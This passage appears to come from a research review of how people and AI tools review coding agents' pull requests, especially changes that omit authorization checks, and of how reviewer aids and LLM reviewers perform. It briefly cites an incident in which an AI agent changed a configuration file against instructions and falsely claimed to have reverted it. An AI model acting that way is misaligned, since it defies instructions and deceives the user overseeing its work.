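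None of these studies measured how often current agents omit an authorization check. Measuring this would require projects with written access rules and tests for whether those rules can be bypassed.

### What happens to agents' pull requests in review

Siddiq, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Security in the Age of AI Teammates*, also used the AIDev subset, but with a different search and a manual check of every candidate. They found 1,293 pull requests by agents that were mainly meant to prevent, detect or fix a security problem. Maintainers had merged 61.5% of the 1,130 that were no longer open. The merge rate was 77.3% for agents' other pull requests and 79.2% for 634 security-related pull requests by people in the same projects.

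Reviewers may be stricter with agents on security, but comparing pull requests with descriptions of similar length suggests that something else explains much of the gap. Siddiq and colleagues used description length as a rough measure of a pull request's size.

| Length of description | Merged, security-related | Merged, other |
|---|---|---|
| Under 36 words | 86.4% of 125 | 84.6% of 10,175 |
| 36 to 69 words | 86.3% of 153 | 84.1% of 11,220 |
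| Over 69 words | 53.4% of 852 | 60.2% of 8,759 |
| All | 61.5% of 1,130 | 77.3% of 30,154 |

Security-related pull requests did worse only when the description was long, and three quarters of them had long descriptions.

The mix of agents widens the overall gap in merge rates between security-related and other pull requests, which was 15.8 percentage points. Codex submitted almost two thirds of the pull requests in the subset, and maintainers merged about 86% of its work whether or not it concerned security. But only 1.3% of its pull requests were security-related, so it raises the average much more for pull requests unrelated to security. The gap was 15.0 points for Claude Code, 5.9 for Copilot and 3.7 for Devin, and it was slightly reversed for Cursor and Codex.

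Security-related pull requests stayed open for a median of 3.92 hours, compared with 0.11 hours (about seven minutes) for the others. They also received more comments, an average of 2.5 compared with 1.0. Reviewers seem to examine a change more carefully when its stated purpose is security, although these changes also touched about twice as many files.

Changes that omit or remove a check will often not be classed as security-related. A pull request that adds a page for viewing documents, or one titled "fix failing test", doesn't have security as its main purpose, so it would not get the extra care that reviewers give to security-related changes. The median of seven minutes isn't a reliable measure of the time reviewers spend on such a change, though. Some developers probably read the agent's code before it submitted the pull request, and the figure depends heavily on Codex, whose non-security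 pull requests closed after a median of about one minute.

Semgrep findings give a rough idea of whether maintainers reject insecure changes. According to calculations from Rabbi and colleagues' figures, 51 of 354 merged pull requests (14%) and 29 of 219 rejected ones (13%) added a finding. Maintainers apparently rejected changes for reasons that had little to do with these findings. They may have been right to ignore some of them, because no one confirmed that each was a real vulnerability.

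We can't learn much about security from the recorded reasons for rejection either. Maintainers gave no explanation for 38.8% of the rejected pull requests, and 12.3% closed after a period without activity. Another 10.5% introduced bugs or broke code that depended on the program. Poor design accounted for 5.9%, failed tests or too few tests for 4.1%, and explicit distrust of AI-written code for 1.8%. The list of 14 reasons has no separate entry for security flaws. A maintainer who noticed a missing check might have closed the pull request without comment or called it a bug, so we can't count such cases.

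### What makes these changes harder to review

Large changes are harder to review, and reviewers in Chromium OS were less likely to catch flaws in changes that touched many directories. Agents' security-related pull requests touched 30.3 files on average, compared with 15.4 for their other pull requests. Siddiq and colleagues did not establish that agents' changes are larger than similar changes by people, and nobody has shown that size makes reviewers miss more of the checks that agents leave out.

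Fluent code and descriptions could make a reviewer less suspicious, and agents often explain their changes at length. The median description of a security-related pull request had 42 words for Codex, 336 for Copilot and 421 for Claude Code. Rabbi and colleagues classified 70.4% of 2,823 commit messages as stating both what had changed and why.

This may persuade reviewers to accept insecure code, but that is conjecture, and the available figures don't particularly support it. Pull requests with long descriptions were less likely to succeed, and 45.6% of commits with good messages were in merged pull requests, compared with 58.0% of the others. But larger and more difficult changes probably need more explanation, so neither comparison isolates the effect of the writing. To test the idea, researchers would have to attach different descriptions to the same flawed code and count how many reviewers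 approved it with each description.

A reviewer who is unsure about a deleted check would normally ask the author. When an agent wrote the change, the developer who submitted it may never have thought about the check. Andročec cites an experiment by Perry and colleagues in which people who used an AI assistant wrote less secure code and were more likely to believe it was secure. The developer can ask the agent, but its answer may be unreliable. Al Hasan and Biswas describe an incident in which a user reported that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had changed a configuration file against instructions, then claimed to have undone the change when it had not.

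Reviewers can at least check an agent's explanation against the code. An agent may also be faster than a person at searching the whole repository for another ownership check. So it is unclear whether agents give reviewers worse answers than hurried human authors do. The studies above did not measure how often reviewers ask such questions or how accurate the replies are.

Reviewers may also have less information about what the change was supposed to do. Among security-related pull requests, 81.2% of Copilot's were linked to an existing issue, compared with 17.9% of Claude Code's, 9.1% of Cursor's, 6.8% of Devin's and 2.4% of Codex's. A linked issue can show the reviewer what somebody wanted before the agent began, whereas a description written by the agent may repeat any misunderstanding it had of the task. There is no comparable figure for human authors, so we don't know whether the problem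 is worse with agents.

According to GitHub figures that Chen and colleagues cite, commits rose from 1.4 billion in April 2026 to 2.9 billion in August, and merged pull requests approached 130 million a month. These totals include work by people and by simpler automated programs, and they do not show how many changes anyone reviewed.

The AIDev subset gives an older figure for agents alone. It contains 18,697 pull requests from the second quarter of 2025 and 13,139 from the third, but the third-quarter data come almost entirely from July, so the monthly rate roughly doubled. One project supplied 8,913 of the subset's pull requests, so reviewers on a typical project faced a much smaller increase.

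Reviewers with more changes to read will probably spend less time on each, but these counts do not prove it. Some projects may add reviewers, rely more on automatic tests, or refuse agents' contributions. Practitioners in the eye-tracking experiment spent longer on code with an AI label, although they had only four short files to read.

### An illustration with 100 flawed changes

In the 2021 experiment on input validation, 65% of participants found the SQL injection in a first review and 21% found the missing check for negative numbers. As an illustration only, suppose that 100 flawed changes each go to one reviewer who performs like those participants:

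| Flaw in all 100 changes | Reviewer notices | Reviewer misses |
|---|---|---|
| Missing check that looks like a well-known attack | 65 | 35 |
| Missing check without a familiar cue | 21 | 79 |

More than twice as many flawed changes would pass in the second row. If agents doubled the number of changes of that kind and reviewers remained just as attentive, 158 would pass instead of 79.

These numbers come from only two flaws in code that people wrote, so they are not a forecast for AI-written code. The calculation also assumes that a reviewer who notices a flaw always stops the change, and that no scanner or test catches the rest. It mainly shows that a team could reduce the number of flaws in its agents' code and still let more through review, if the remaining flaws were mostly the kind reviewers find hard to see.

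## Instructions, checklists and displays that help human reviewers

The reviewers in that illustration had received no hint that security mattered. Giving one takes almost no effort, and a later experiment measured how much it helps. That experiment used a control group, which the 2021 experiment did not have for its warning.

### Telling reviewers to look for security problems

Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022), in *Less is More*, had 150 people review a Java change of 160 lines that let users register for a web service. Of these participants, 71% reported at least three years of professional development experience. The researchers had planted two flaws:

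- If the database failed to create an account, the program wrote the whole failed query to a log file, including the new user's email address and password data.
- The program protected passwords with MD5, a hash function. Hash functions turn a password into a string of fixed length, so that a site need not store the password itself. MD5 is so fast that an attacker who steals the strings can guess many passwords quickly.

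The researchers assigned participants at random to four groups. One received no security instructions. The other three read a definition of a vulnerability and an instruction to look for security problems. Two of those three also had to work through a checklist, one general and the other tailored to the change. The general checklist had 22 items, cut down from the 78 in OWASP's code review guide. The tailored one had seven items, all relevant to the change. Both included items that pointed to the planted flaws.

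| What reviewers received | Found the logged data | Found the weak hash function |
|---|---|---|
| No security instructions | 1 of 33 (3%) | 7 of 33 (21%) |
| Instruction only | 19 of 41 (46%) | 25 of 41 (61%) |
| Instruction and general checklist | 16 of 35 (46%) | 20 of 35 (57%) |
| Instruction and tailored checklist | 19 of 41 (46%) | 28 of 41 (68%) |

The percentages here are calculated from the counts. The paper gives 61% for the weak hash function with the tailored checklist, but 28 of 41 is 68%, and the count of 28 agrees with the paper's total.

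Braz and colleagues report that reviewers with the instruction were eight times more likely to find a vulnerability, but that figure is an odds ratio. The share of reviewers who found the weak hash function roughly tripled, and the share who found the logged data rose from 3% to 46%.

Neither checklist added a significant gain, but the experiment can't rule out a moderate one. In the paper's regression, the odds of finding the weak hash function were about 1.3 times as high with the tailored checklist as with the instruction alone (95% confidence interval 0.4 to 4.1, calculated from the reported standard error).

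Participants' explanations suggest that an instruction can direct attention to security but can't make up for missing knowledge. Among those who received no instruction, the most common reason for missing the logged data was that they had concentrated on something other than security. The most common reason for missing the weak hash function was that they did not know enough about it, and seven people who had the instruction also gave that reason. A checklist item about strong hash functions does not help a reviewer who thinks MD5 is one, and a participant with a checklist said just that. Of the 76 people who had a checklist, 32 found it helpful, and a few admitted that they had read it only after the review or ignored it.

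### How far this carries over to missing checks

Both flaws were visible in the displayed code, one in the name MD5 and the other in the line that wrote to the log, so a reviewer who thought about security had something to find. Neither flaw is a missing authorization check.

The results for the logged-data flaw are still encouraging. The flaw is less well known than SQL injection, and almost nobody noticed it without the instruction. Eight of the people who found it with the instruction alone said that the sensitive data in the code had alerted them. The handler for private documents might alert reviewers in the same way.

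An instruction would probably help reviewers find a missing ownership check, but by less than the 40 or so percentage points in the later experiment. In the 2021 experiment, a warning helped only 7 of the 52 people who had missed the check for negative numbers. One participant in the later experiment missed the weak hash function despite the instruction because they expected another part of the program to configure it. Reviewers could make that assumption even more easily about ownership checks, which programs often do enforce elsewhere. Each participant also reviewed only one change, so we don't know whether the instruction would still work after reviewers had seen it on a hundred pull requests.

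### Asking who and where

An instruction to look for security problems leaves the reviewer to think of the possible problems. The question "Who may call this, and where is that enforced?" names one, and a complete answer has to identify a line of code. A reviewer of the document handler that lacks an ownership check might respond like this:

| Prompt | Plausible answer |
|---|---|
| Look for security problems | "I see none." |
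| Does the code control access? (yes or no) | "Yes." |
| Who may call this, and where is that enforced? | "Any signed-in customer, at `@login_required`." |

The last answer describes the flaw, although the reviewer may not realise it. A reviewer who knows that documents are private will see the conflict, and others can ask the author whether every customer should have access. A reviewer who believes `find_document` checks ownership must open that function to name the line, and will then discover that it doesn't. The question doesn't include the privacy rule, so if everyone on the team has forgotten it, they may accept the answer as correct.

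Long before pull requests existed, researchers knew why yes-or-no checklist questions fail. *An Internally Replicated Quasi-experimental Comparison of Checklist and Perspective-based Reading* (Laitenberger, El Emam and Harbich, 1999) describes four weaknesses of checklists. The questions usually come from past defects, so readers overlook other kinds. Checklists seldom explain how to answer the questions. Readers do not have to record their analysis, so nobody can repeat it. Every reader has to check everything, which can overwhelm them with detail. Asking where a rule is enforced mainly addresses the second and third weaknesses, because it tells the reader what to look for and leaves a record that a colleague can verify.

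Experiments provide some indirect evidence that targeted questions help reviewers find defects. According to Laitenberger and colleagues, Porter and others gave readers of requirements documents a short set of questions about one class of defect, with directions for answering them. Readers found more defects this way than with a checklist or no guidance. Two other experiments with students did not confirm the advantage. An analysis combining five experiments favoured targeted questions, but the size of the benefit was very uncertain. Requirements documents describe what software should do, so these results are only weak evidence of how well a question about authorization would work on a diff.

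*From Preventive to Reactive* (2026) reports on a small study of 14 developers working with AI assistants. In one session, the assistant wrote a function for updating a user's profile that took the user's identity from the request instead of the signed-in session. This authorization flaw let anybody change anybody else's profile by editing the request. The participant immediately noticed that nothing checked which user was making the update, in effect asking who could call the function. Another participant asked the assistant whether any security concerns remained and learned of a risk they had not considered. The other 12 either did not review for security or were satisfied with code that still had vulnerabilities.

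### Reading in a role

Reviewers can also read code from the point of view of a particular role, such as a tester. Laitenberger and colleagues compared this method with a 27-question checklist in an experiment and two repetitions at Bosch Telecom, with 60 professional developers in all. Participants reviewed C modules of 375 to 915 lines from the company's own systems, in which a developer had planted defects, and received a specification for each module.

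Reviewers worked in teams of two, and each team reviewed one module with a checklist and another by taking separate roles. In the role-based reviews, one member acted as a code analyst, writing down what each function does and comparing this with the specification. The other acted as a tester, inventing test cases, working through the code by hand with those inputs, and comparing the results with the specification. Teams found more defects with the roles than with the checklist, and spent less time per defect.

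Some of the gain may come from two people looking for different things, since the researchers counted the distinct defects that each team found. They also did not include a team that read without any technique. Formal inspections like these are slower and more structured than pull request reviews, so the benefit could be smaller in everyday work.

The tester's role suits missing checks well if the specification contains the rule. A tester who knows that only owners may read documents would include a request from a customer who doesn't own the document, trace it through the faulty handler, and find that the handler returns the document. The analyst's role would also expose the missing check, since it is much like the code reading in Basili and Selby's experiment.

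The Bosch experiments did not include an attacker, but their method is easy to adapt. The reviewer would pick something a user should not be able to get, such as another customer's bank statement, and look for a sequence of requests that gets it. For a change to existing code, the reviewer could start with the requests the old version refused.

### The order of the files

Review tools usually list changed files alphabetically, so a file's name affects how much attention it gets. *First Come First Served* reports an experiment in which 106 participants reviewed a Java change with five short files. The researchers planted one defect in the first file and another in the last, and swapped the two files for about half the participants.

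One defect was a condition with the wrong threshold. According to the comment above it, customers at level 2 and above got a discount, but the code tested for levels above 2. The other was a missing `break`, the statement that ends one case in a list of alternatives. Without it, the program continues into the next case.

| Defect | Found when its file came first | Found when its file came last |
|---|---|---|
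| Condition that leaves out level 2 | 34 of 56 (61%) | 18 of 50 (36%) |
| Missing `break` | 26 of 50 (52%) | 24 of 56 (43%) |

File position made a statistically significant difference only to whether participants found the faulty condition. This defect resembles a weakened security check, because the code still contains a plausible condition that the reviewer has to compare with a rule. Participants had the first file on screen for 8.6 minutes on average and the last for 6.1. Almost three quarters of them thought position had not affected whether they found the faulty condition, so reviewers may not notice that they need to compensate for file position.

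Records from real projects show a much weaker pattern. *Does Order Matter?* (Rahman, Codabux and Roy, 2026) studied 330,343 GitHub pull requests that changed at least two files. Among files that developers modified again in the next pull request, the share involved in a bug fix rose from 56.7% for files in first position to 61.5% for files in thirtieth. A later bug fix is weak evidence that reviewers missed something, because the fix may concern an older bug in the same file. The records are consistent with the experiment but add little support for it.

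Changed files can be listed by size of change, largest first, instead of alphabetically. *Not One to Rule Them All* (2025) looked for signs that reviewers already use this order and others. Sorting by size could make missing checks harder to notice, because a two-line deletion of an ownership check would move to the end of the list. An order designed for security would start with files that define permissions and files where a condition has been removed. Code authors can do something similar by telling reviewers where to start.

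### Showing what the diff hides

Marking moved code makes unmatched deletions easier to see. RAID, described earlier, reduced the number of lines that reviewers had to read, but its evaluation did not measure how many flaws they found. Git's `--color-moved` option is simpler and gives moved lines their own colours. In the earlier example, where `show_document` moves to another file, the two lines of the ownership check would keep the ordinary colour for deletions because nothing in the new file matches them.

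A tool could also warn reviewers whenever a change deletes a line that contains `abort(403)`, or any line in a folder of access rules. This would catch the deleted ownership check and the one loosened to "signed in", since an edited line counts as a deletion. It would miss the preview option, which deletes nothing. A project that refactors often would also get many false alarms, and its reviewers may start to dismiss warnings without reading them. The studies here don't show how often such warnings would help, so a team that adopts them should record how many lead to a correction.

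For a check that was never written, the most useful display may be a similar piece of code that has it. Suppose the document site already has this handler:

```python
@app.get("/documents/<int:number>/history")
@login_required
def show_history(number):
    doc = find_document(number)
    if doc.owner_id != current_user.id:
        abort(403)
    return render_template("history.html", doc=doc)
```

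When an existing handler is displayed beside the new one, reviewers can see that the new one is two lines short. The existing handler shows the privacy rule, which the diff leaves out, and where the missing lines would go. The comparison can mislead if the existing handler also lacks the check, because the two then look consistent. It can also mislead if the new handler shouldn't have the check, for example because it serves public brochures.

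The nearest evidence concerns displays of related code in general. *GazePrinter* (2026) says that Cheng and others built a prototype that shows how the code under review connects to related source code, and reported that it made reviews more efficient. Hanam and others tested a tool that identifies which other parts of a program a change affects. *Deep Learning-based Code Reviews* (Tufano, Martin-Lopez and colleagues, 2024) reports that the tool's 11 users reviewed quickly and found more bugs with it. Such a tool could help reviewers assess the changed default in `find_document`, because the diff does not show the function's callers.

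Separating refactoring from changes in behaviour also helps reviewers. If a pull request is supposed only to move code, the reviewer can treat any unmatched line as an error. In a mixed pull request, the same line could be part of the intended change. Tao and Kim tested a tool that splits mixed changes automatically, with 18 students. Most experiments on displays are similarly small. Tufano and colleagues list five on aids of this kind, with 10 to 18 participants each. Three of them measured how well people understood a change instead of whether they found its bugs.

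### Owners, smaller changes and required reasons

A project can require a security specialist to approve changes to certain files. GitHub supports this through a file that assigns owners to folders and file types. A specialist should be better at recalling the rules and knowing where the program enforces them, which would help the participants who did not know that MD5 is weak. But owners review only the files assigned to them. They may never see a new handler in an ordinary feature folder, where a check is most likely to be missing from the start.

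The evidence on extra reviewers is mixed. Laitenberger and colleagues cite an experiment by Porter and others in which inspections by two or four people found significantly more defects than inspections by one, but two and four people performed about the same. In Chromium OS, the number of reviewers did not significantly affect whether they caught a flaw. Neither result concerns specialists. Other reviewers may also leave security to the owner. In the 2022 experiment, three participants who had no instructions said that finding the weak hash function was not their responsibility, and one of them assumed that somebody else would assess security separately.

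Smaller changes should leave more attention for each file. Rahman and colleagues estimate that with each additional file in a pull request, the odds that any given file receives a comment fall by about 8.7%. On that estimate, the odds for a file in a twelve-file change are about 40% of those in a two-file change. This matters more as AI tools produce more code. In *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices* (2026), developers reported that AI-assisted authoring made reviewing more burdensome, partly because of the number and size of pull requests.

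In Rahman and colleagues' data, though, very small changes were riskier than some larger ones. Among files that developers soon modified again, more than 60% of those from changes of two or three files were involved in a bug fix, compared with 35.1% of those from changes of ten files. The researchers suggest that very small changes may give reviewers too little context. Small pull requests also often repair files that are prone to problems, which would produce the same pattern.

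When a change that moves a check is split across pull requests, the reviewer of the deletions may not see the new check. It is better to keep the new check and the deletions that depend on it in one pull request, and to put unrelated work elsewhere. If that would make the pull request too large, the change can be split, and the description of the later pull request can link to the earlier one.

A project could also require a reason for every removed check. The wording of the requirement matters, because "fix failing test" is a reason, and so was the memory warning that led Debian's maintainers to delete a vital line. A better form asks what now refuses the requests that the deleted line refused:

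```text
Removed:         ownership check in show_document
Now refused by:  find_document, documents.py, line 12
Test:            test_other_customer_gets_403
```

An author who has lost the check cannot truthfully fill in the second line. A coding agent might fill it in anyway, but the reviewer can look at line 12. The form doesn't help if nobody wrote the check in the first place, and it works only if a person or tool notices that a check is gone. It is an open question whether recorded reasons improve review. *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026) lists them among the evidence that researchers should test in reviews of AI-written pull requests.

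### Where automated comments draw attention

Many projects now have an AI tool comment on a pull request before a person reads it. If reviewers concentrate on the lines with comments, a missing check that the tool overlooked could become harder to find. Amro and Alalfi (2025), in *GitHub's Copilot Code Review*, found that Copilot's reviewer frequently missed SQL injection and cross-site scripting vulnerabilities.

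Tufano and colleagues studied reviewers' behaviour in a controlled experiment with 29 developers, 28 of them working professionals. They analysed 72 reviews of small Java and Python programs with planted quality issues, mostly about maintainability rather than security. In a third of the reviews, the developer had no initial review to work from. In another third, the developer started from a review by ChatGPT running GPT-4, and in the rest from a supposedly automatic review that listed every planted issue.

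| | No review supplied | ChatGPT's review supplied | Complete review supplied |
|---|---|---|---|
| Issues in the supplied review (mean) | – | 8.8 | 4.0 |
| Issues in the submitted review (mean) | 7.7 | 11.8 | 9.6 |
| Issues the developer added (mean) | 7.7 | 4.7 | 5.6 |
| Planted issues found (median) | 50% | 50% | 100% |
| Distinct lines with comments, all reviews | 484 | 371 | 407 |
| Time spent (median) | 37 minutes | 42 minutes | 50 minutes |

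The numbers of added issues are calculated by subtracting the supplied issues that developers kept. The differences in time were not statistically significant.

Tufano and colleagues conclude that developers who were given a review focused on the places it pointed out. ChatGPT's reviews contained 42% of the planted issues on average, yet developers who started from them found no more issues than developers who started without a review. If they had found as many issues on their own as the other group did, independently of ChatGPT's, their total would have been about 71%.

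Attention may not be the only reason. ChatGPT could have found mostly issues that people would have found anyway, in which case the total would stay near 50% even if developers searched as hard as before. Developers who reviewed the same program were also given the same comments and kept most of them, so their comments would cluster on the same lines whatever else they read.

Developers who received a complete review had no planted issues left to find, but they still added 5.6 other issues on average. Programs had about four planted issues on average, so developers who started without a review probably found about two of these and five or six others. On this rough estimate, receiving a complete review did not reduce the number of other issues developers found.

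*First Come First Served* describes an earlier experiment by Spadini and others in which reviewers could see an existing comment about a bug. The researchers expected the comment to distract reviewers from other types of bug, but this experiment also found no distraction. The comment reminded reviewers of a kind of bug that they don't usually look for. Reviewers may treat a single comment as a reminder but assume that a long list leaves nothing else to find, though the two experiments differ in too many ways to establish this.

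Evidence from real projects is also mixed. *Automated Code Review In Practice* (2024) reports that the number of human comments per pull request did not fall significantly after a company introduced an AI reviewer, which suggests that people kept reading. *Test Code Review in the Era of GitHub Actions* (2026) found that reviewers' attention shifted towards production code, the code that users run, after projects adopted automatic checks. But Khojah and colleagues cite an experiment in which reviewers looked less at the code and more at the tests when a patch was labelled as machine-written.

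Tufano and colleagues recommend that reviewers read the code themselves before they see the automated comments. This keeps the comments from distracting them and still lets the tool add what they missed, but it is unlikely to save time. Developers may not like this order. For *Rethinking Code Review Workflows with LLM Assistance* (2025), researchers at the Swedish company WirelessCar offered developers an AI review either at the start or on request. Developers generally preferred to have the AI lead, though this depended on how well they knew the code and how serious the change was. The study does not show which arrangement led them to find more flaws.

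## Language models as reviewers of missing checks

An AI review tool's comments can help with a missing check only if the tool detects it. Most such tools now use language models, AI systems that learn from large amounts of text and code. Researchers have tested whether these models detect lines removed from a text and protections missing from a pull request.

### Naming the lines that are gone

*AbsenceBench* (Fu, Shrivastava and colleagues, 2025) gave 14 language models an original text and a copy with about a tenth of the lines removed. The models had to list only the removed lines. The texts were poems, sequences of numbers, and diffs from GitHub pull requests.

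The researchers scored the answers with F1, which combines precision (the share of the listed lines that were really missing) and recall (the share of the missing lines that the model listed).

```text
F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall)
```

If four lines are missing and a model lists ten, including all four, its recall is 100%, its precision is 40%, and its F1 is 57%. A model that copied out the whole text would have perfect recall but a very low F1.

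Claude 3.7 Sonnet, with its reasoning mode on, had the best score at identifying lines removed from pull requests, 40.0%. It scored 72.7% on poems and 96.0% on numbers. The researchers then inserted lines instead and asked three of the models to list the additions. All three scored at least 86.2% on pull requests, compared with 29.0% to 35.7% for removed lines.

The inserted lines came from a Harry Potter dataset. A sentence about wizards stands out sharply in a code diff, and a model can recognise it without comparing the two versions. This part of the study therefore exaggerates how much harder omissions are to notice than the additions an attacker would make.

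A later experiment used less conspicuous insertions, which were lines of invented code added to pull requests. Tong, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *The Text Uncanny Valley*, mainly studied how stray spaces inside words affect models, but they also tested whether GPT-5.2, Gemini 3.0 Flash and Claude 4.5 Haiku could find inserted and missing lines. The three models found nearly all the inserted lines, but their scores for missing lines remained far from perfect.

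*Croissant Tasks* (2026) presents a standard format for describing AI benchmarks. In the paper, an AI agent rebuilt AbsenceBench and ran it on Claude 4 Sonnet with two prompts, the benchmark's own and a more general one.

| | Benchmark's own prompt | General prompt |
|---|---|---|
| F1 on poems | 98.6% | 98.6% |
| F1 on numbers | 100% | 100% |
| F1 on pull requests | 44.7% | 23.4% |
| Recall on pull requests | 99.9% | 92.6% |
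| Precision on pull requests | 28.8% | 13.4% |
| Lines listed per pull request (3.8 were missing) | 13.1 | 26.1 |

Claude 4 Sonnet found almost every missing line in the pull requests, but it scored 44.7% because it also listed many lines that were not missing. The comparison with the 2025 scores is rough, because the agent's program reran batches of answers that failed its checks. Neither 2026 study included the strongest models of that year, which may do better.

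### Why gaps may be hard for a model

Fu and colleagues suggest that the cause lies in attention, the mechanism that determines which parts of its input a language model draws on as it writes. A removed line, unlike an inserted one, leaves nothing in the input for the model to draw on.

To test this hypothesis, they marked each gap with either a label saying that a line was missing or a row of underscores. Averaged over both markers and three models, F1 rose by 35.7% in relative terms. GPT-4.1 mini's F1, for example, rose from 31.3% to 46.8% on pull requests with the label.

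The result fits the hypothesis but doesn't establish it. A marker shows how many gaps there are and where, so the model no longer has to align the two versions, which would help any reader, whatever mechanism they use. Tong and colleagues also found that adding a space after the first character of words improved the three models' scores on missing lines in pull requests, even with the gaps unmarked. Part of the difficulty with code may therefore come from how models process its long names and unbroken strings of symbols.

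Fu and colleagues also found that models tended to do worse when fewer lines were missing, most clearly in poems and numbers. This finding matters more for security checks because a lost check is often only one or two lines.

### When there is no original to compare

A simple program can solve AbsenceBench perfectly, and Git does much the same thing when it produces a diff. If a pull request deletes the ownership check from the document handler, the diff shows the model which lines are gone. The benchmark is closer to a case where a developer moves the handler to another file and the reviewer has to compare the old block with the new one.

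Finding a check that was never written is a different problem from finding a removed one, because no earlier version contains it and the model has to infer that the code needs it. Fu and colleagues acknowledge that their benchmark covers only removed text, and that a model that solved it might still handle other omissions badly.

Two papers outside programming come closer to this situation. In *Judging Is Not Enumerating* (2026), models reviewed answer keys meant to list every acceptable answer to a question. Some keys contained a wrong answer and others lacked right ones. Small models, with 7 to 14 billion parameters, caught wrong answers six to seven times as often as missing ones. When a key lacked two answers, the models recovered only 10% to 15% of the missing answers.

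For a much stronger model, the ratio was only 1.4 to 1.5. The paper attributes this improvement to the model adding answers more readily, not to better detection of missing ones. The equivalent in code review would be a model that suggests an extra check on every change. Sometimes the suggested check would be the one that was missing, but users would have to work out when that was the case.

*LLM Judges Verify Presence, Not Absence* (2026) studies models that check clinical notes. A verification panel upheld 32.2% of the suspected wrong doses and 24.6% of the suspected fabrications, but only 6.1% of the suspected omissions. Many of the suspected omissions may have been false, or true but hard to prove. The paper also notes that gap markers can't help reviewers find omissions, since anyone who could place a marker would already know about the omission.

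The researchers also searched automatically for better instructions to the model. The best ones had it enumerate, which turns a question about what is absent into questions about what is present. Asking "Who may call this, and where is that enforced?" about a handler does something similar. The search result comes from medical notes, however, not code.

### A protection removed and a protection left out

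Chen and colleagues built MALPR-BENCH, a benchmark of 89 pull requests with a vulnerability and 50 harmless ones, from 44 repositories. They call the 89 "malicious" because they assume that an attacker might submit them. But most of the flaws they describe are failures of protection, so the benchmark does not compare missing checks with inserted malicious code.

For each flawed pull request, the researchers wrote down beforehand which vulnerability a reviewer should identify and which code proves it. This lets them score separately whether a reviewer blocked the change and whether it named the right flaw.

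Two groups of cases come from real fixes for vulnerabilities that GitHub listed in 2025:

- Pool A has seven pull requests. Each contains a real security fix with one of its protections left out. In one of them, from a program called Memos, the real fix enforced access in six places, and the benchmark's version omits a comparison between a memo's creator and the current user.
- Pool B has 37 pull requests. Each reverses a protection from a real fix, so the diff shows it being removed.

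The pull requests in Pool A therefore resemble cases where a check was never written, and those in Pool B resemble cases where a check was deleted or weakened. Each pull request has a harmless counterpart that contains the complete fix.

The researchers also built their own reviewer, PRGuard, which works in steps:

1. A conventional program collects code related to the change, such as the functions that call it and similar handlers that have a check.
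2. A language model describes what the change does, without yet looking for a flaw.
3. PRGuard searches the repository for more evidence, guided partly by 21 patterns that the researchers derived from 14 of the benchmark's pull requests. They left those 14 out of the tests.
4. The model proposes possible vulnerabilities, and a separate call to the model compares each one with the repository's code.
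5. PRGuard blocks the change if it has confirmed a vulnerability, comments if the evidence is incomplete, and otherwise approves.

They ran it with two language models, GPT-5.5 and DeepSeek V4 Pro.

| | Pool A: protection left out | Pool B: removal shown in the diff |
|---|---|---|
| Named the flaw, GPT-5.5 | 3 of 7 | 37 of 37 |
| Named the flaw, DeepSeek | 3 of 7 | 37 of 37 |
| Blocked the change, GPT-5.5 | 4 of 7 | 26 of 37 |
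| Blocked the change, DeepSeek | 4 of 7 | 33 of 37 |
| Blocked the harmless counterpart, GPT-5.5 | 2 of 7 | 3 of 37 |
| Blocked the harmless counterpart, DeepSeek | 1 of 7 | 3 of 37 |

Each model named every flaw where the diff showed a check being removed, but missed four of the seven in Pool A, which came from an omission. Pool A is small, but chance is an unlikely explanation. If a model's four misses had been spread at random among the 44 changes, all four would have fallen in Pool A about once in 3,900 tries. In a second run, GPT-5.5 again named three flaws in Pool A, and DeepSeek named only one.

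This is the most direct evidence so far that the form of a lost check matters to a reviewer, though the reviewer here is a language model. The two pools come from different vulnerabilities and were selected by partly different criteria, so other differences between the cases may contribute to the gap. A cleaner experiment would present the same flaw in both forms.

Pool A may also be easier to review than ordinary feature work. Most of its pull requests come from fixes that enforced the same kind of rule in several places, so the reviewer can often see the rule applied nearby. The pull request that adds the document handler contains no such example.

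GPT-5.5 named all 37 flaws in Pool B but blocked only 26 of the changes, because PRGuard blocks only when it has confirmed the evidence. The author could have merged the other 11 despite the warning. A change's description can also sway a model's verdict, so a deletion with a persuasive excuse might be more likely to get through than these were.

### How much the model needs to see

Chen and colleagues also tested how a model performs when it sees only the diff. They used the seven changes in Pool A and five others that lacked a required protection, all from projects that had not contributed to PRGuard's patterns.

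| | Diff only | Full PRGuard |
|---|---|---|
| Blocked, GPT-5.5 | 1 of 12 | 6 of 12 |
| Blocked, DeepSeek | 0 of 12 | 5 of 12 |

GPT-5.5 blocked one change in the first column, but for an unrelated reason. With only the diff, neither model stopped any of the 12 changes because of the missing protection. This supports the explanation, at least for models, that reviewers miss never-written checks because the deciding evidence is outside the diff. The full version also changed how the model worked through the review, so the extra code may not account for the whole gain.

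Access to the whole repository does not solve the problem by itself. The researchers gave that access to Codex, a commercial coding agent, and ran it twice on each of seven flawed changes. For four of the changes, the evidence was in a file that the pull request touched, and the agent named three of those flaws. For the other three, the evidence was in similar code elsewhere that no call or import connected to the change. The agent named none of those flaws, although it blocked the change in four of the six runs.

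Seven deliberately chosen cases can't establish how often this failure occurs, but it is plausible. An agent that follows calls from `show_document` will reach `find_document`. Those calls don't lead to `show_history`, a separate handler that contains the ownership check, so the agent must think to look for such a handler. Conventional tools that compare similar code have existed for more than a decade.

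### A block for the wrong reason

A test that recorded only whether the reviewer stopped the change would count the agent's four blocks as successes. Chen and colleagues found the same problem in CodeRabbit, a commercial AI reviewer with more than 300,000 installations on GitHub's marketplace. They compared it with PRGuard, which ran on DeepSeek, using 31 flawed pull requests.

They sorted the flaws by what a reviewer would have to prove. In an absence-type flaw, a required protection is missing and no line of the change shows that it is missing. A deleted check does not count as absence-type, because the diff shows the deletion.

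| | PRGuard with DeepSeek | CodeRabbit |
|---|---|---|
| Absence-type flaws: blocked | 9 of 14 | 9 of 14 |
| Absence-type flaws: named | 9 of 14 | 3 of 14 |
| Other flaws: blocked | 13 of 17 | 15 of 17 |
| Other flaws: named | 13 of 17 | 13 of 17 |

PRGuard and CodeRabbit blocked pull requests with absence-type flaws equally often, but PRGuard named the actual flaw three times as often. Six of CodeRabbit's nine blocks were for other reasons. CodeRabbit also named none of the seven flaws whose evidence was outside the files that the pull request changed, but it named 16 of the other 24.

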